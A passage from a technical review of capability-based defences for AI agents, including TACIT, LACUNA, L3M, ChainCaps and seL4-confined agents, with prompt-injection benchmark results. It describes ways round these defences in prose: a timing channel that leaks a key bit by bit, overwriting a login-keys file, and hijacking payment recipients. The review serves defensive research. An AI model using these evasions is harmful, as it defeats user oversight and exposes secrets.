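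### File handles that can't leave their block

Access to files in TACIT lasts for one block of code. The function `requestFileSystem` opens a folder, passes the block a capability for it, and ends the access when the block finishes. This program tries to keep the access for later:

```
val later = requestFileSystem("invoices") { fs =>
  () => fs.access("0412.txt").read()
}
```

The block returns a function that would read the invoice whenever the program called it. That function has `fs` in its capture set, but `fs` exists only inside the block. The function therefore has no valid type outside the block, and the compiler rejects the program. Every file handle that comes from `fs` also has `fs` in its capture set, so it can't leave either. E needs a membrane to catch such handles, but Scala's compiler catches them without wrappers. As with a membrane, text the program has already read can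 still leave the block.

The folder name is still a string that the model writes. According to Glama's *TACIT* page, which reproduces the project's documentation, the library checks the name at run time against a list of allowed folders, which by default contains only the directory where the server started. The agent can open a new block for an allowed folder at any time, so the end of a block doesn't permanently revoke access. To grant narrower access, a developer can define specific objects in advance, such as one document database and one output file, and leave out the function that requests others.

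### Safe mode and the trusted base

Ordinary Scala has features that would defeat capture checking, such as unchecked casts, which could make a function that holds a file look pure. Scala's *Safe Mode* page describes a restricted version of the language for code from agents. This version bans unchecked casts and pattern matches, annotations that silence such checks, runtime reflection, and a module of deliberately unsafe features. It also requires capture checking throughout, including for changes to variables, and lets programs use global library objects only if they are safe too.

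Library authors can exempt their own code by marking it `@assumeSafe`. Scala's example is an email object that shows the user each message and sends it only if the user agrees. The object uses an unrestricted mailer internally, but an agent can reach the mailer only through this approval step. Nothing verifies that the marked code is safe, so whoever adds the mark has to make sure it is. Joe-E's list of permitted library methods placed the same burden on its authors.

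Exceptions are still allowed because almost any operation can cause one, for example by dividing by zero or running out of memory. An exception thrown inside `map` could reveal something about the hidden text, so TACIT catches the exception and turns it into an ordinary value, which it can wrap like any other. Safe mode also prevents exceptions from carrying capabilities out of a block.

Users of TACIT have to trust:

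- the Scala compiler, including capture checking and safe mode
- TACIT's library and the wrappers around individual tools
- the runtime that executes compiled programs
- the second model, if they use one, and the service that runs it, which must not keep the text or pass it on.

The hosted model is outside the trusted base, and Odersky and colleagues assume that it may cooperate fully with an attacker. The shared part of the library is about 1,000 lines long, but the compiler is much larger. In March 2026, according to lampepfl's *TACIT* documentation on GitHub, TACIT searched each program for forbidden patterns instead of using the compiler's safe mode. By October it had an option to use both.

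### The leak experiment

Odersky and colleagues tested whether agents would reveal secrets from a Scala project containing a directory of API keys, a database and confidential documents. They paired each of 12 ordinary tasks with each of 10 prompt injections, for 120 trials. In 11 more trials, the user asked for the secrets outright or posed as somebody entitled to them, such as an administrator in an emergency. Each model ran all 131 trials twice, once with the secrets in `Classified` and once with them as plain text.

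| | Claude Sonnet 4.6 | MiniMax M2.5 |
|---|---|---|
| Leaks with wrapping | 0 of 131 | 0 of 131 |
| Leaks without wrapping, injections | 0 of 120 | 3 of 120 |
| Leaks without wrapping, malicious users | 2 of 11 | 8 of 11 |
| Trials without a leak, no wrapping | 98.5% | 91.6% |
| Tasks completed with wrapping | 99.2% | 90.0% |
| Tasks completed without wrapping | 83.3% | 88.3% |

The zero leak counts follow almost directly from the type rule. A trial counted as a leak if secret text appeared in the agent's output, and the wrapper prevents that unless the compiler or the library has a bug. The trials were therefore a fairly mild test for such bugs. Some injections contained ready-made Scala code for reading the secret files, but a determined attacker would look for flaws in capture checking itself.

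The completion rates are more informative, because they don't follow from the type rule. Agents could summarise a confidential incident report or anonymise staff reviews without seeing the text. This doesn't mean that wrapping makes agents better at their work, because Odersky and colleagues suspect that Sonnet's low score without wrapping comes partly from the set-up. The model often ran out of time or turns, and sometimes stopped to warn the user about an injection.

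AgentDojo is a harder test in one respect, because other researchers wrote it. Odersky and colleagues adapted its four groups of tasks to TACIT and ran 963 attacks on each of two models, Gemini 2.5 Pro and o4-mini-high. One attack succeeded, against o4-mini-high. The user had asked the agent to book one hotel, and the attacker had planted a recommendation for another in the first hotel's reviews. The agent booked the right hotel but quoted the reviews to the user, and AgentDojo's automatic check counted the other hotel's name as a success for the attacker. This hardly counts as a failure of TACIT, because its policy allowed the agent to show the user public reviews.

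The adapted tools return emails, chat messages, web pages and reviews as `Classified`, so in most cases the agent never read the injection. The low attack rate is therefore better evidence for keeping untrusted text away from the agent than for the compiler's ability to block what a misled agent tries. The instructions for these tasks also tell the agent that side effects inside `map` happen immediately, and that it should put them exactly where it wants them. This suggests that the adapted version let some actions, perhaps including payments, run inside `map`. If so, it lacked capability completeness, and its results are weak evidence for local purity.

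Odersky and colleagues describe TACIT's completion rates on AgentDojo as comparable to CaMeL's. With Gemini 2.5 Pro, that is about right except on travel tasks, where TACIT completed 64.3% and CaMeL 1.4%. With o4-mini-high, CaMeL did better in all four task groups. The gap was wide on office tasks, where CaMeL completed 81.4% and TACIT 52.9%, and on Slack tasks, where CaMeL completed 68.6% and TACIT 47.6%.

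### What writing Scala costs

To test whether the language itself hurts performance, Odersky and colleagues compared agents that wrote Scala with agents that called the same tools in the usual way. They used τ²-bench, which simulates conversations with customers of an airline and a shop, and SWE-bench Lite, which consists of 300 real bugs from public software projects.

| Model and benchmark | Ordinary tool calls | TACIT |
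|---|---|---|
| gpt-oss-120b, airline | 43.8% | 45.2% |
| gpt-oss-120b, retail | 53.3% | 57.0% |
| MiniMax M2.5, airline | 58.4% | 61.0% |
| MiniMax M2.5, retail | 75.1% | 77.5% |
| DeepSeek V3.2, airline | 57.8% | 58.6% |
| DeepSeek V3.2, retail | 74.6% | 75.5% |
| MiniMax M2.5, SWE-bench Lite | 43.3% | 41.7% |

The drop on SWE-bench Lite is five bugs out of 300, which could easily be chance. On τ²-bench, between 0.3% and 7.9% of programs needed another attempt after an error, and one or two retries usually fixed them. Typical mistakes were unrelated to security, such as treating a dollar sign as an ordinary character in Scala strings where it has a special meaning.

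These models could evidently write the required Scala. But the tools in τ²-bench returned plain data, so the comparison doesn't measure how much worse agents perform when data is hidden from them. The AgentDojo results give a better idea of this, and the drop looks considerable for some models.

### LACUNA

With TACIT, an ordinary agent sends programs to a server. Zhao, Xu and colleagues (2026), in *LACUNA*, a paper from May by the same group, put the model inside the program instead. A developer leaves a gap and states what type of value should fill it:

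```
def unpaidTotal(folder: InvoiceFolder): Double =
  agent("Add up the unpaid invoices")
```

When the program reaches the gap, LACUNA sends the model the task, the expected type, the surrounding code, and the names and types of everything available at that point. The model replies with Scala code. LACUNA compiles this code as if the developer had typed it there, and runs it if it has type `Double`. If it doesn't compile, the model receives the errors and tries again, up to a limit.

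In LACUNA, a tool is a function that the code can name. With capture checking and safe mode on, the names in scope at the gap determine what the agent can access. The code above can use `folder`, but it can't send email because nothing in scope gives it access to a mail server. A developer can put a network capability in scope at one step and leave it out at the next. Both protections are optional, and without safe mode the model's code could use reflection or start an external program without holding any capability.

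LACUNA also makes `Classified` data more useful. In TACIT, the agent has to write the function for `map` without knowing what the text contains. In LACUNA, that function can contain a gap of its own, which a trusted local model fills after reading the text. The local model's code also has to be pure, so it can adapt to an unusual invoice but can't send the invoice anywhere.

Zhao and colleagues also show what happens when the model makes a mistake halfway through. A variable `balance` holds 100, and the task is to subtract 50 and return the new balance as an integer. The model writes:

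```
balance -= 50
s"remaining: $balance"
```

The last line produces a string, so the code has the wrong type. A harness that ran the code line by line would subtract the 50 before reaching the error, and a retry might subtract it again. LACUNA compiles both lines together before running either, so it rejects them both and the balance stays at 100. This protects only against errors that the compiler can find. If code compiles, makes a payment and then crashes because a server is down, the payment has still gone through.

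On BrowseComp-Plus, a set of 830 difficult research questions about a fixed collection of documents, LACUNA with DeepSeek-V4-Flash answered 27.1% correctly. The compiler rejected 8.6% of the model's code, or 0.7 retries per question. Zhao and colleagues conclude that the checks don't reduce accuracy, but they didn't run the same model on these questions without LACUNA, so the result can't support this conclusion.

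The LACUNA paper compares LACUNA with ordinary tool calls on τ²-bench. With the same DeepSeek model, LACUNA solved 76.0% of 392 tasks and ordinary tool calls solved 90.0%. The difference is about 55 tasks, most of them in retail and telecom, though the paper describes the results as "on par". On retail, the compiler rejected 22.4% of the model's code. A weaker model, Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite, solved 29.1% with LACUNA and 33.2% with ordinary tool calls, and the compiler rejected 89% of its code on the standard telecom tasks.

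Oddly, Scala slightly improved performance on this benchmark with TACIT but reduced it with LACUNA. The two papers tested different models, and LACUNA ran its models with reasoning turned off and only one attempt per task. LACUNA also runs the whole conversation as a series of gaps, which may be harder for a model than calling a Scala tool from a familiar loop. Zhao and colleagues suspect that the models' training data contained too little Scala, but that alone wouldn't explain why TACIT did better.

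On AgentDojo, eight of 1,898 attacks succeeded against LACUNA, seven of them with Gemini 2.5 Pro. Zhao and colleagues point out that the type system can't stop an attacker who persuades the model to misuse a capability that the task requires.

### What the type checker misses

Although a pure function can't send a message, Odersky and colleagues accept that an agent could use one to leak a bit of a secret by making its running time depend on that bit. TACIT's optional time limit makes this easier, because the agent receives an error when a program exceeds it. An agent could submit a function that loops forever if the first bit of a key is 1 and stops at once if it is 0. Whether the agent received an error would reveal the bit without a clock, and 256 such programs would reveal a 256-bit key. Local purity therefore provides non-interference only against observers who can't tell how long a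 program took or whether it finished.

Many harmful programs also compile without any trick. `Classified` keeps text secret but doesn't protect files from changes. As Glama's page warns, an agent can wrap any text in `Classified` and write it over a confidential file, such as the list of keys accepted for logging in to the user's machine, if that file is in an allowed folder. A setting blocks these writes, but it is off by default. TACIT also lets programs send wrapped data to approved web hosts, so an agent can log in to a service with a password it can't read. If an attacker has an account on the same host, an injected instruction might get the agent to send the data to that account.

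Types also don't show whether an action is the right one. A program that pays the wrong supplier has the same type as one that pays the right supplier. Zhao and colleagues would like to add types for limits, such as a maximum amount, and have a proof tool such as Lean check them. That would help only with rules that somebody can write down. Neither system's types control what an external command does once the agent starts it, so the list of permitted commands is the only limit there.

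All of this depends on capture checking, a compiler feature that Scala's documentation calls "still highly experimental and unstable". In a forum thread, *Capture leak when using varargs?*, a user reported that the compiler had accepted code that capture checking should have rejected. The reply explained that the compiler would even have let the function be declared pure, a mistake that would defeat the protection `Classified` provides. The developers prepared a fix. The user later saw the problem again in a newer version, though another reply suggested that capture checking might not have been switched on. Researchers have machine-checked proofs for the core of the type system, but Odersky and colleagues say that safe mode still needs its own proof.

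For security-critical systems, the TACIT paper recommends running TACIT inside a conventional sandbox. If a compiler bug let a program escape TACIT's checks, the sandbox could still keep it from reading the user's login keys. The sandbox would not stop the program from reading a confidential invoice and sending it to the hosted model, because the agent needs both the file and the connection to the model for its ordinary work.

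## Can agents delegate and write new tools without gaining authority?

TACIT checks the programs that an agent writes for its current task. An agent that works for days may also keep a program as a permanent tool or hand part of its job to another agent. Either step could give it more authority than the user granted, for instance if the new tool can reach the network or the second agent starts with fresh permissions. Several papers from 2026 prove that, under certain conditions, neither step can add authority, and most of the proofs share one simple argument.

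### Grants that can only shrink

The simplest way to compare grants is to treat each one as a set of permitted effects. One grant is no stronger than another if its effects are a subset of the other's. An agent may give another agent only a grant no stronger than its own, and a trusted program outside the model checks every request to delegate.

Suppose three agents handle the invoices. The user gives the coordinator the root grant G0. The coordinator creates a reader, and the reader creates a formatter:

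```
G0 (coordinator) = {read invoices, write summary, mail the accounts office}
G1 (reader)      = {read invoices, write summary}
G2 (formatter)   = {write summary}
```

Both delegations pass the check, because G1 is a subset of G0 and G2 is a subset of G1. Suppose an injected instruction in an invoice then leads the reader to request a helper with the grant {read invoices, mail the accounts office}. This request fails the check because the reader isn't allowed to send that mail, so it can't pass the permission on, even though the coordinator has it.

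The general proof is by induction on the number of delegations between an agent and the user. The root grant, G0, is a subset of itself. If an agent's grant lies within G0 and the agent passes on a subset of it, the new grant also lies within G0. Therefore, no chain of delegations can produce a grant outside G0. If a checkpoint also compares every call with the caller's grant, no agent in the team can directly do anything that G0 doesn't permit.

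Wei and Xiong (2026), in *Access Control for Agentic AI*, give this proof in a few lines. Their grants can also contain obligations, such as getting approval before sending mail, and a delegated grant must keep all its parent's obligations. In the token system of Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao, a delegated token keeps the same action and resource. Its lifetime and number of uses can't increase, and the number of further delegations it allows must fall each time, so every chain ends. Whenever an agent uses a delegated token, the gateway checks each link back to the original. *A Five-Plane Reference Architecture for Runtime Governance of Production AI Agents* argues for a similar bound, but only informally.

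Cancelling a grant should cancel everything derived from it. *DelegateGuard* does this. In five of its test workflows, a worker tried to finish a transfer after the user had cancelled the task. A fixed list of allowed destinations let all five transfers through, while DelegateGuard blocked them.

These designs give a tighter bound than the reference graph did. In the graph, any member of a connected group could send its references to any other, so non-amplification held only for the group as a whole. In these designs, a trusted program records who holds each grant, and an agent can't transfer a grant by putting it in a message. The reader and everything beneath it therefore stay within G1. CapScope lacks this property because it compares new grants only with the ceiling for the whole team. Even the tighter bound covers only permissions, so the formatter may still be able to write a note that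 persuades the coordinator to send mail.

When an agent lends part of a numerical limit to a child, the harness has to subtract that amount from the agent's own limit. Comparing sets of permissions isn't enough, because a coordinator allowed 100 model calls could give two children limits of 100 each. Neither child's grant would exceed its parent's, but together they could make 200 calls. With subtraction, a coordinator that lends 40 calls to one child and 30 to another should have 30 left.

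### L3M and its tokens

In *L3M*, Eisenach, George and colleagues (2026) describe a harness that follows these rules and lends model calls in this way. They built it at Amazon and published it in September. L3M is written in Lean 4, a programming language and proof assistant, so programmers can write a function and prove properties of it in the same language. A small program called the kernel checks the proofs. L3M's theorems are therefore about checks in the code that runs, whereas the EROS proof was about a separate model of the system.

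When an agent starts, the harness reads the agent's grant from a record that the agent can't edit. It then creates one token for each kind of access in the grant. A token is a Lean value that includes its limits. A file token lists the agent's folders, and a network token lists the hosts the agent may contact. Only the module that defines a type of token can create tokens of that type.

Tools reach the outside world through effect classes, which are groups of operations such as reading files or fetching web pages. Each operation takes a token as an argument. In simplified form, the network operation looks like this:

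```
fetch : NetworkToken -> Request -> Response
```

A tool without a network token can't form a network call. The harness offers the model only the tools whose tokens the agent holds, so it doesn't offer a web tool to an invoice assistant without network access. The model still writes addresses and file names as text, and the harness supplies the tokens. When a tool makes a call, the code that contacts the operating system checks the token's limits again.

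### Programs that become tools

An L3M agent can save a Lean program in its own folder and use it as a tool the next time it starts. The invoice assistant might write one to add up the totals, so that the model doesn't have to read every file:

```
description: "Add up the totals of all invoices"
footprint:   [read files]
run:         open each invoice, find its total, return the sum
```

The footprint is the program's permission request, and it is part of the program's type. That line shows that the program can read files but can't change them or use the network. Lean's type checker enforces this by making only the declared operations available inside `run`. A program that calls `fetch` won't compile unless it declares network access, and even if it does compile, the harness won't offer it to an agent without a network token.

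Compiling Lean source can run code, so the harness first inspects the program's syntax and rejects anything but a single expression of a restricted form. It then checks that the program uses no unsafe features, creates no tokens and adds no axioms.

These programs can't run a shell or call a model directly, but they can start other agents, and the usual check on grants applies. Eisenach and colleagues suggest using this to read untrusted web pages. The program fetches a bug report, starts an agent with an empty grant and asks it whether the report describes a fault in a particular component. The program accepts only "yes", "no" or "unclear" and treats any other answer as "unclear". An instruction injected into the report could cause a wrong answer, but its text couldn't reach the first agent.

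In *Agent libOS*, Zhang (2026) aims for the same result with run-time checks instead of types. Agents can write tools in TypeScript, create children, and save and restore their own state without gaining permissions over existing resources. The system checks each operation against the agent's permissions, the limits of its task, its budget and any required approval. Saved state may contain a permission that the user has since revoked, so when Agent libOS restores an agent, it keeps only what both the saved and current permissions allow. In a suite of 33 tasks, Zhang found no unauthorised effects and no wrongly refused requests. These results cover only the tested cases, whereas L3M's theorems cover all inputs to the checks they describe.

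### What the theorems cover

| L3M's guarantee | What Lean's kernel has checked | What the build enforces or users must assume |
|---|---|---|
| File tools stay in the agent's folders | The text of an accepted path never leads out of them | Run-time code has to deal with links in the file system |
| Delegation adds no authority | A child's first grant lies within its parent's, each descendant's lies within an extended version of the root's, and no agent can issue itself a grant | The proof covers records that agents can write, not a human's later changes |
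| Tokens require a grant | Start-up creates tokens only for access that the grant includes | Checks during the build prevent forgery, without a proof |
| Children borrow their budgets | After one batch of loans, the children's limits and the parent's remainder add up to no more than the parent had | Later loans and repayments need a further proof |
| Agent-written programs add no authority | An accepted program directly names only approved functions and constants | Lean must process the source safely, and the code behind the approved functions must be correct |
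| Risky calls get a review | With default settings, the harness reviews every call to a tool if it can't undo the effects and no token limits them | The effect classes must be correctly labelled, and the reviewer can still be wrong |
| File edits are reversible | Undoing a recorded edit restores the original bytes | Git, which stores the old version, must return what it saved |

Under L3M's theorem about descendants, every descendant's grant lies within the root's stored grant plus the Git branches and mail belonging to each of its ancestors. The addition is necessary because each agent can use its own branches and mailbox even though its stored grant doesn't list them. If an agent gives a child access to these, the child's grant contains something that the root's stored grant does not. Without the addition, the theorem would therefore be false after a single delegation, and L3M's source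 code includes a counterexample.

Grants can also change after an agent has started, and the harness checks each new grant against the issuer's own grant. In the invoice team, the coordinator could later let the formatter mail the accounts office, even though the reader between them can't send that mail. The new grant is within G0, so the bound for the whole team still holds, but the formatter's authority is no longer within G1.

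The rule against forged tokens depends on a linter, a program that inspects the code during every build. It runs after Lean has resolved all the names, so an alias can't hide a forbidden call. Users have to trust the linter, along with Lean's compiler, six small C files, the Linux kernel, Git and several other programs.

Each theorem in Eisenach and colleagues' paper concerns one check, and they argue informally that the checks together confine an agent. They don't claim a theorem about a whole session, and no theorem shows that a malicious program can't harm the machine while the harness loads it. The theorems also don't rule out an agent misusing the authority it already has. If an agent can read a private key and push files to a server, it can send the key there, and all the theorems still hold.

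### L3M against Claude Code

Eisenach and colleagues measured how much these restrictions hinder an agent on 37 tasks from Terminal-Bench, a benchmark of jobs that agents complete on a Linux machine. They compared L3M with Anthropic's coding agent Claude Code, with its permission checks turned off. Both used Claude Opus 5 and had three attempts at each task.

L3M calls a tool "tame" if the harness can undo its effects or a token limits its reach in advance. Its shell tool meets neither condition, so by default a second model reviews each shell command. If the two models still disagree after a short exchange, a human decides. The tests replaced the human with a fixed answer of yes or no.

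| Set-up | Solved within three attempts | Tokens per successful attempt |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Code | 59.5% | 4.4 million |
| L3M with a shell, no review | 41.7% | 7.7 million |
| L3M with a shell and review, disagreements approved | 40.5% | 12.1 million |
| L3M with a shell and review, disagreements rejected | 43.2% | 12.8 million |
| L3M with tame tools only | 27.0% | 7.7 million |
| L3M with tame tools, no agent-written programs | 24.3% | 6.2 million |

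Eisenach and colleagues emphasise that L3M solved about two thirds as many tasks with tame tools alone as it did with a shell. The loss looks larger when counting successful attempts, which fell from 34 to 18. With tame tools, L3M solved fewer than half as many tasks as Claude Code. That gap isn't all due to narrower authority, because L3M was 18 percentage points behind even with a shell. Nobody had tuned L3M's prompts or tool descriptions, and Claude Code's shell could also reach the internet.

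The test provides almost no evidence that writing new tools helps. The difference between 27.0% and 24.3% is one task out of 37, though five of the 18 successful attempts with tame tools used agent-written programs.

Review made little difference to the success rate but roughly doubled the number of model calls. Each reviewed command took about 2.6 extra calls and typically 8.6 seconds. The models eventually judged about 90% of shell commands safe, replaced 6% with tame tools, and disagreed on 2.4%. Terminal-Bench tests whether agents finish their work, so these figures don't measure how many attacks the reviewer would catch.

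### Authority that changes with experience

L3M lets an agent's tools change while its grant stays the same. Users may also want to widen a grant as an agent proves reliable. Zhang and Zhang (2026), in *Are You Still the Agent I Authorized?*, a theoretical paper from July without measurements, allow this below a fixed ceiling B that the user sets at the start. The agent's active authority at time t can shrink freely and can grow when evidence, such as a record of passed tests, meets the grant's conditions. The monitor intersects any proposed authority with the ceiling:

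P(t) = P_proposed(t) ∩ B

Let Req(a) be the effects that the monitor believes an action a will have, and Eff(a) the effects it really has. The proof is a chain of inclusions:

Eff(a) ⊆ Req(a) ⊆ P(t) ⊆ B

The first inclusion is an assumption about what the monitor knows. The monitor checks the second before allowing the action, and the intersection guarantees the third. Zhang and Zhang add an induction along the chain for delegated authority, as in the three-agent example.

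If the agent can produce the evidence itself, requiring evidence doesn't tighten the bound. An attacker who controls a coding agent can have it pass enough tests to earn everything up to B, so the security guarantee is B from the first day. To keep part of B out of the attacker's reach, the grant needs a condition that the agent can't satisfy alone, such as a person's signature. This is a serious objection to schemes that remove an agent's last limits after a good record, because an attacker can aim for the final stage from the start.

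Zhang and Zhang also let the user specify which changes leave a grant in force. For example, switching to another company's model might suspend the grant even if the new model would have the same permissions. A ceiling on effects can't express this rule, because the ceiling doesn't depend on who is acting.

### Chains of individually permitted calls

*ChainCaps* (Jiang, Yang and colleagues, 2026) describes an agent that has to prepare a report. It reads a salary spreadsheet, fetches industry figures from the web, summarises both and emails the summary to a distribution list. Its grant permits each call, but the salaries were meant to stay inside the company.

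A theorem about delegation can't rule this out, because every call lies within the root grant. Non-interference fails here, as in the earlier payroll example. The agent needs to read the salaries and send mail, and a grant that is only a set of effects can't permit both while forbidding mail that contains salaries.

ChainCaps therefore places limits on data. Each value has a "budget", which in this system means the set of destinations it may still reach. Despite the system's name, a budget is closer to one of CaMeL's labels than to a capability. When a tool combines values, the result gets the intersection of their budgets:

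```
salaries         = {show to user}
industry figures = {show to user, send by mail}
summary          = {show to user}
```

If a tool t produces y from the inputs x₁ to xₖ, the full rule is:

B(y) = Pass(t) ∩ B(x₁) ∩ ... ∩ B(xₖ)

Pass(t) is a limit that the tool's description sets on the tool's output. Before any call that sends or writes data, a proxy between the agent and its tools checks the destination against the budget of every value that contributed to that data. The agent can show the summary to the user but can't email it.

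The proof again uses induction, over the steps that produce a value. Intersection never adds a destination, so a value may go only where all of its sources may go. The exception is a signed, single-use token that releases a particular value to a particular destination.

The language model makes this harder, because the proxy can't tell which parts of the prompt influenced the model's output. ChainCaps assumes they all did. It keeps one budget for the model's whole context, and that budget shrinks whenever the model reads something more restricted. Once the agent has read the salaries, it can't send mail about anything else either, unless the proxy resets the context budget. The proxy blocked 45% of a set of difficult but legitimate tasks, or 20% if it reset the budget between tasks.

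Jiang and colleagues tested ChainCaps with five models on 56 attacks and 26 legitimate tasks, running each three times. ChainCaps cut the attack success rate from between 25% and 68%, depending on the model, to at most 4.8%, and the agents still completed at least 96% of the legitimate tasks. The attacks concentrated on failures of this kind, so the rates don't show how often such failures happen in ordinary use. Many of the attacks that still succeeded involved shell commands or scripts that moved data where the proxy couldn't see it.

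A single permitted call can also leak data. With DelegateGuard's protections in place, 9 of 45 attacks in a test with realistic conversations still leaked data, all through code reviews. The worker had permission to post its review as a public comment, and it posted details of an unpublished security flaw. *DelegateGuard* includes a short proof that no check can prevent this if it ignores both the content and amount of the data. Such a check must treat a harmless comment and a harmful one the same way if the two calls are otherwise identical.

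### What the proofs take for granted

All of these bounds require complete mediation, meaning that every effect passes through the check. The shell commands in the ChainCaps tests broke this condition. An agent with general network access could also break it by contacting a service directly instead of through the gateway. Wei and Xiong cite a 2026 survey of 7,973 reachable MCP servers, about 40% of which offered tools without any authentication. Those servers wouldn't reject such a call.

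The check also needs a correct description of what each call does. Wei and Xiong require descriptions that list every possible effect, including effects that depend on the arguments. If a grant permits mail only to Alice, the description "sends mail" isn't specific enough, and their system would refuse the call. In Zhang and Zhang's example of an outdated description, a coding agent has permission to run tests on its own machine. Its harness then loads, without notifying the monitor, a new tool that sends test results to a remote server. The monitor keeps approving test runs, each of which now sends data out, and no theorem limits how many times this can happen.

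Jiang and colleagues measured how much descriptions matter. When experts wrote the descriptions, ChainCaps blocked every attack in that test and allowed all the legitimate work. With descriptions written using a checklist, it blocked 90.9% of attacks. With naive descriptions, it blocked only 27.3% and also stopped half of the legitimate tasks. L3M partly avoids this problem for tools written in Lean, because the type checker compares the footprint with the code, but somebody still has to describe the effect classes correctly.

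A stranger's description of a tool may be deliberately false. *Formal Analysis and Supply Chain Security for Agentic AI Skills* (Bhardwaj, 2026) reports that researchers found 341 malicious add-ons among the 2,857 then listed in the marketplace for OpenClaw, a popular open-source agent. Bhardwaj's tool, SkillFortify, analyses whether an add-on can exceed the access it declares. On a benchmark of 270 malicious and 270 harmless add-ons, it missed about 20 of the malicious ones and raised no false alarms. But its analysis of information flow caught nothing that simple pattern matching had missed, so the result is weak evidence about the formal method's value.

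Finally, the root grant has to be right, because the induction starts from it. The tests of *DelegateGuard* included 45 attacks, and none succeeded when the root grant contained only what the task needed. The researchers then added one external web address to that grant "for convenience", and 30 attacks succeeded. The other 15, which tried to use cancelled grants, still failed. In all 30 successful attacks, every delegated grant was within its parent's, as the theorem requires.

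## How much harm does a narrow grant stop, and what harm remains?

Even a correct root grant permits some attacks, because an injected instruction may need only the tools that the user's task requires. Alhindi measured the remaining exposure in *Taming AI Agents with seL4*, the November 2026 paper that is the source of the invoice-agent example described earlier. Its agents run on the seL4 kernel and can call only the functions for which they hold capabilities.

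### Protection domains, channels and badges

Agent frameworks typically run all their agents and tools in one process, so an attacker who hijacks one agent gets the authority of all of them. Alhindi instead puts each agent and each tool in its own protection domain, a program with its own memory and list of capabilities. An agent's domain contains a short loop that sends the conversation to a hosted model and attempts any action the model outputs.

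To call a tool, the domain needs a channel, a capability for sending that tool a request and waiting for the reply. The kernel refuses a call on any channel the domain doesn't hold. In the invoice team, the email agent has a channel to the inbox and no others, so an email with instructions to pay somebody can't directly cause a payment. The bank tool has a separate channel for each of its four functions. One agent can approve payments and another can make them, so neither can complete a payment alone.

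The bank also has to record who approved what, and a hijacked agent might give a false name. Each channel therefore carries a badge, a number set when the capability is created. The kernel delivers the badge with every call, and the caller can't change it. The tool looks up the badge in a table to identify the agent.

Agents hand each other work through pairs of memory regions, one for each direction, and each agent can write only to its own side. Each agent also has its own budget of processor time, so a hijacked agent that floods a tool with calls uses up only its own budget. A developer has to decide all of this before the system starts. For the invoice team, a generator turns a short policy file into 43 channels and 74 memory regions, and nobody can add more while the system runs.

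### The AgentDojo test

Alhindi tested this design on AgentDojo's banking and Slack tasks. The test had 249 attack cases and 37 tasks without an attack, each run three times with gpt-4o-mini. The agent ran in a protection domain with a separate channel for every function it could use, while AgentDojo's simulated bank and chat service ran on an ordinary computer.

One version of the agent held channels for every function, and the other held channels only for the functions in AgentDojo's reference solution to the user's task. The model saw the full list of functions in both versions, so only the capabilities differed.

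| | Every function granted | Only the task's functions granted |
|---|---|---|
| Attacks that succeeded | 48% | 7% |
| Tasks completed without an attack | 68% | 58% |
| Tasks completed under attack | 46% | 43% |
| Attacks that succeeded with a script controlling the agent | 248 of 249 | 67 of 249 |

The drop in attacks is far too large to be chance. Alhindi doesn't find the loss of completed tasks significant (p = 0.27), but 37 tasks are too few to rule out a real loss of ten points or more. Some tasks probably failed because the kernel refused the model's calls to functions that the reference solution didn't use.

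Part of the drop to 7% was luck. Of the 358 attacks that succeeded with every function granted, the narrow grant stopped 233 by blocking a call the attack needed, and 35 succeeded again. The other 90 failed without being blocked, for example because the model ignored the injection that time.

The scripted test removes this luck by replacing the model with a script that does the user's task and then makes every call the attacker's goal requires. In this test, the narrow grant stopped 73% of the attacks that had worked without it. The remaining 27% is a better guide than the 7% to what the grant allows, since a more capable model might carry out attacks that gpt-4o-mini failed to complete.

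Both figures are a best case, because the grants came from reference solutions. Someone writing a grant before knowing the exact task would have to include more functions. Also, seL4's proofs do not cover the build's configuration.

Most of the protection against a misled model probably comes from the narrow grant and would be available without seL4. AgentDojo includes a simpler defence called a tool filter, in which a model uses the user's request to choose the relevant tools before the agent reads any data. *Least-Privilege Auditing of Agent Tool Calls with Intent Graphs and Reasoning-Guided Escalation* (2026) recomputed the filter's results for GPT-4o from published logs. With the filter, attacks succeeded 6.5% of the time and agents completed 69.7% of tasks, compared with 67.1% of tasks without it.

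The filter did worse in *NOMOS* (2026), where 11.8% of attacks succeeded and the completion rate fell from 79.2% to 58.3% because the filter removed tools that the tasks needed. The kernel matters more if an attacker runs code inside the agent, because the attacker could then switch off a filter in the agent's own process but not the kernel's checks.

### When the attack needs the same tool as the task

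Every attack that succeeded against the narrow grant used only functions that the user's task needed. About half used `send_money`. In those cases, the user had asked the agent to pay a bill, so the agent had the function, and the injected text supplied the attacker's account as the recipient. The capability did not limit who could receive the money.

Common agent frameworks have this gap by default. For the June 2026 audit mentioned in the first section, Mellafe Zuvic traced tool calls through specific versions of their public source code. LangChain takes a tool's name from the model's output, looks it up in a table and runs the tool with the model's arguments. LlamaIndex works much the same way.

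Stripe's toolkit lets developers specify which actions are permitted and use keys with restricted rights. Within those limits, it forwards whatever amount, currency and customer the model supplies, so enabling a refund tool authorises refunds in general.

The audit covers only defaults, since developers can add their own checks or approval steps, and it excludes any checks Stripe's remote servers may make. *Delegation Without Trust* (2026) independently reached the same conclusion about LangChain and its companion LangGraph. OpenAI's *Agent security in the enterprise* (2026) similarly warns companies that a valid credential doesn't by itself establish which actions are authorised.

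### A capability to pay one invoice

The object-capability answer is to replace `send_money` with something much narrower. For each invoice, a trusted program creates an object much like the earlier allowance wrapper, with the limit set to the amount of the invoice:

```
def makeInvoicePayment(bank, payee, amount):
    remaining = amount
    return object:
        pay(part) ->
            if not (0 < part <= remaining): fail
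            remaining = remaining - part
            bank.send_money(payee, part)
```

The agent receives this object and has no other access to the bank. An injected instruction to pay the attacker now fails because `pay` has no field for a recipient. The agent can still pay too early, pay an invoice that the user meant to dispute, or not pay at all. But it can't exceed the amount of the invoice, even in instalments. (Unlike the allowance wrapper, this object also rejects the value NaN.)

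This is more work for a tool's designer than splitting the bank into four functions, because the bank tool has to create a new capability for every invoice while the system is running. On seL4, a badge could carry the invoice's number instead of the caller's identity, but Alhindi's system fixes all its channels before it starts. seL4 itself lets programs derive capabilities at run time, though this makes the team harder to check in advance.

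The tool must also keep a record of what it has already paid. Two simultaneous calls must not both spend the same remainder, and a restart must not reset it. If the connection drops after the bank has sent the money, a retry must not send it again. Payment services usually handle this with an idempotency key, an identifier that stays the same across retries so the service can detect repeats. Mellafe Zuvic's checkpoint rejects calls that require such a key but don't have one.

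### Who fills in the payee?

The hardest requirement is that the payee and amount come from a source the attacker can't influence. If the model reads them from a forged invoice, the new capability would authorize payment only to the attacker. Mellafe Zuvic therefore requires that no part of the policy come from a model's output, even indirectly.

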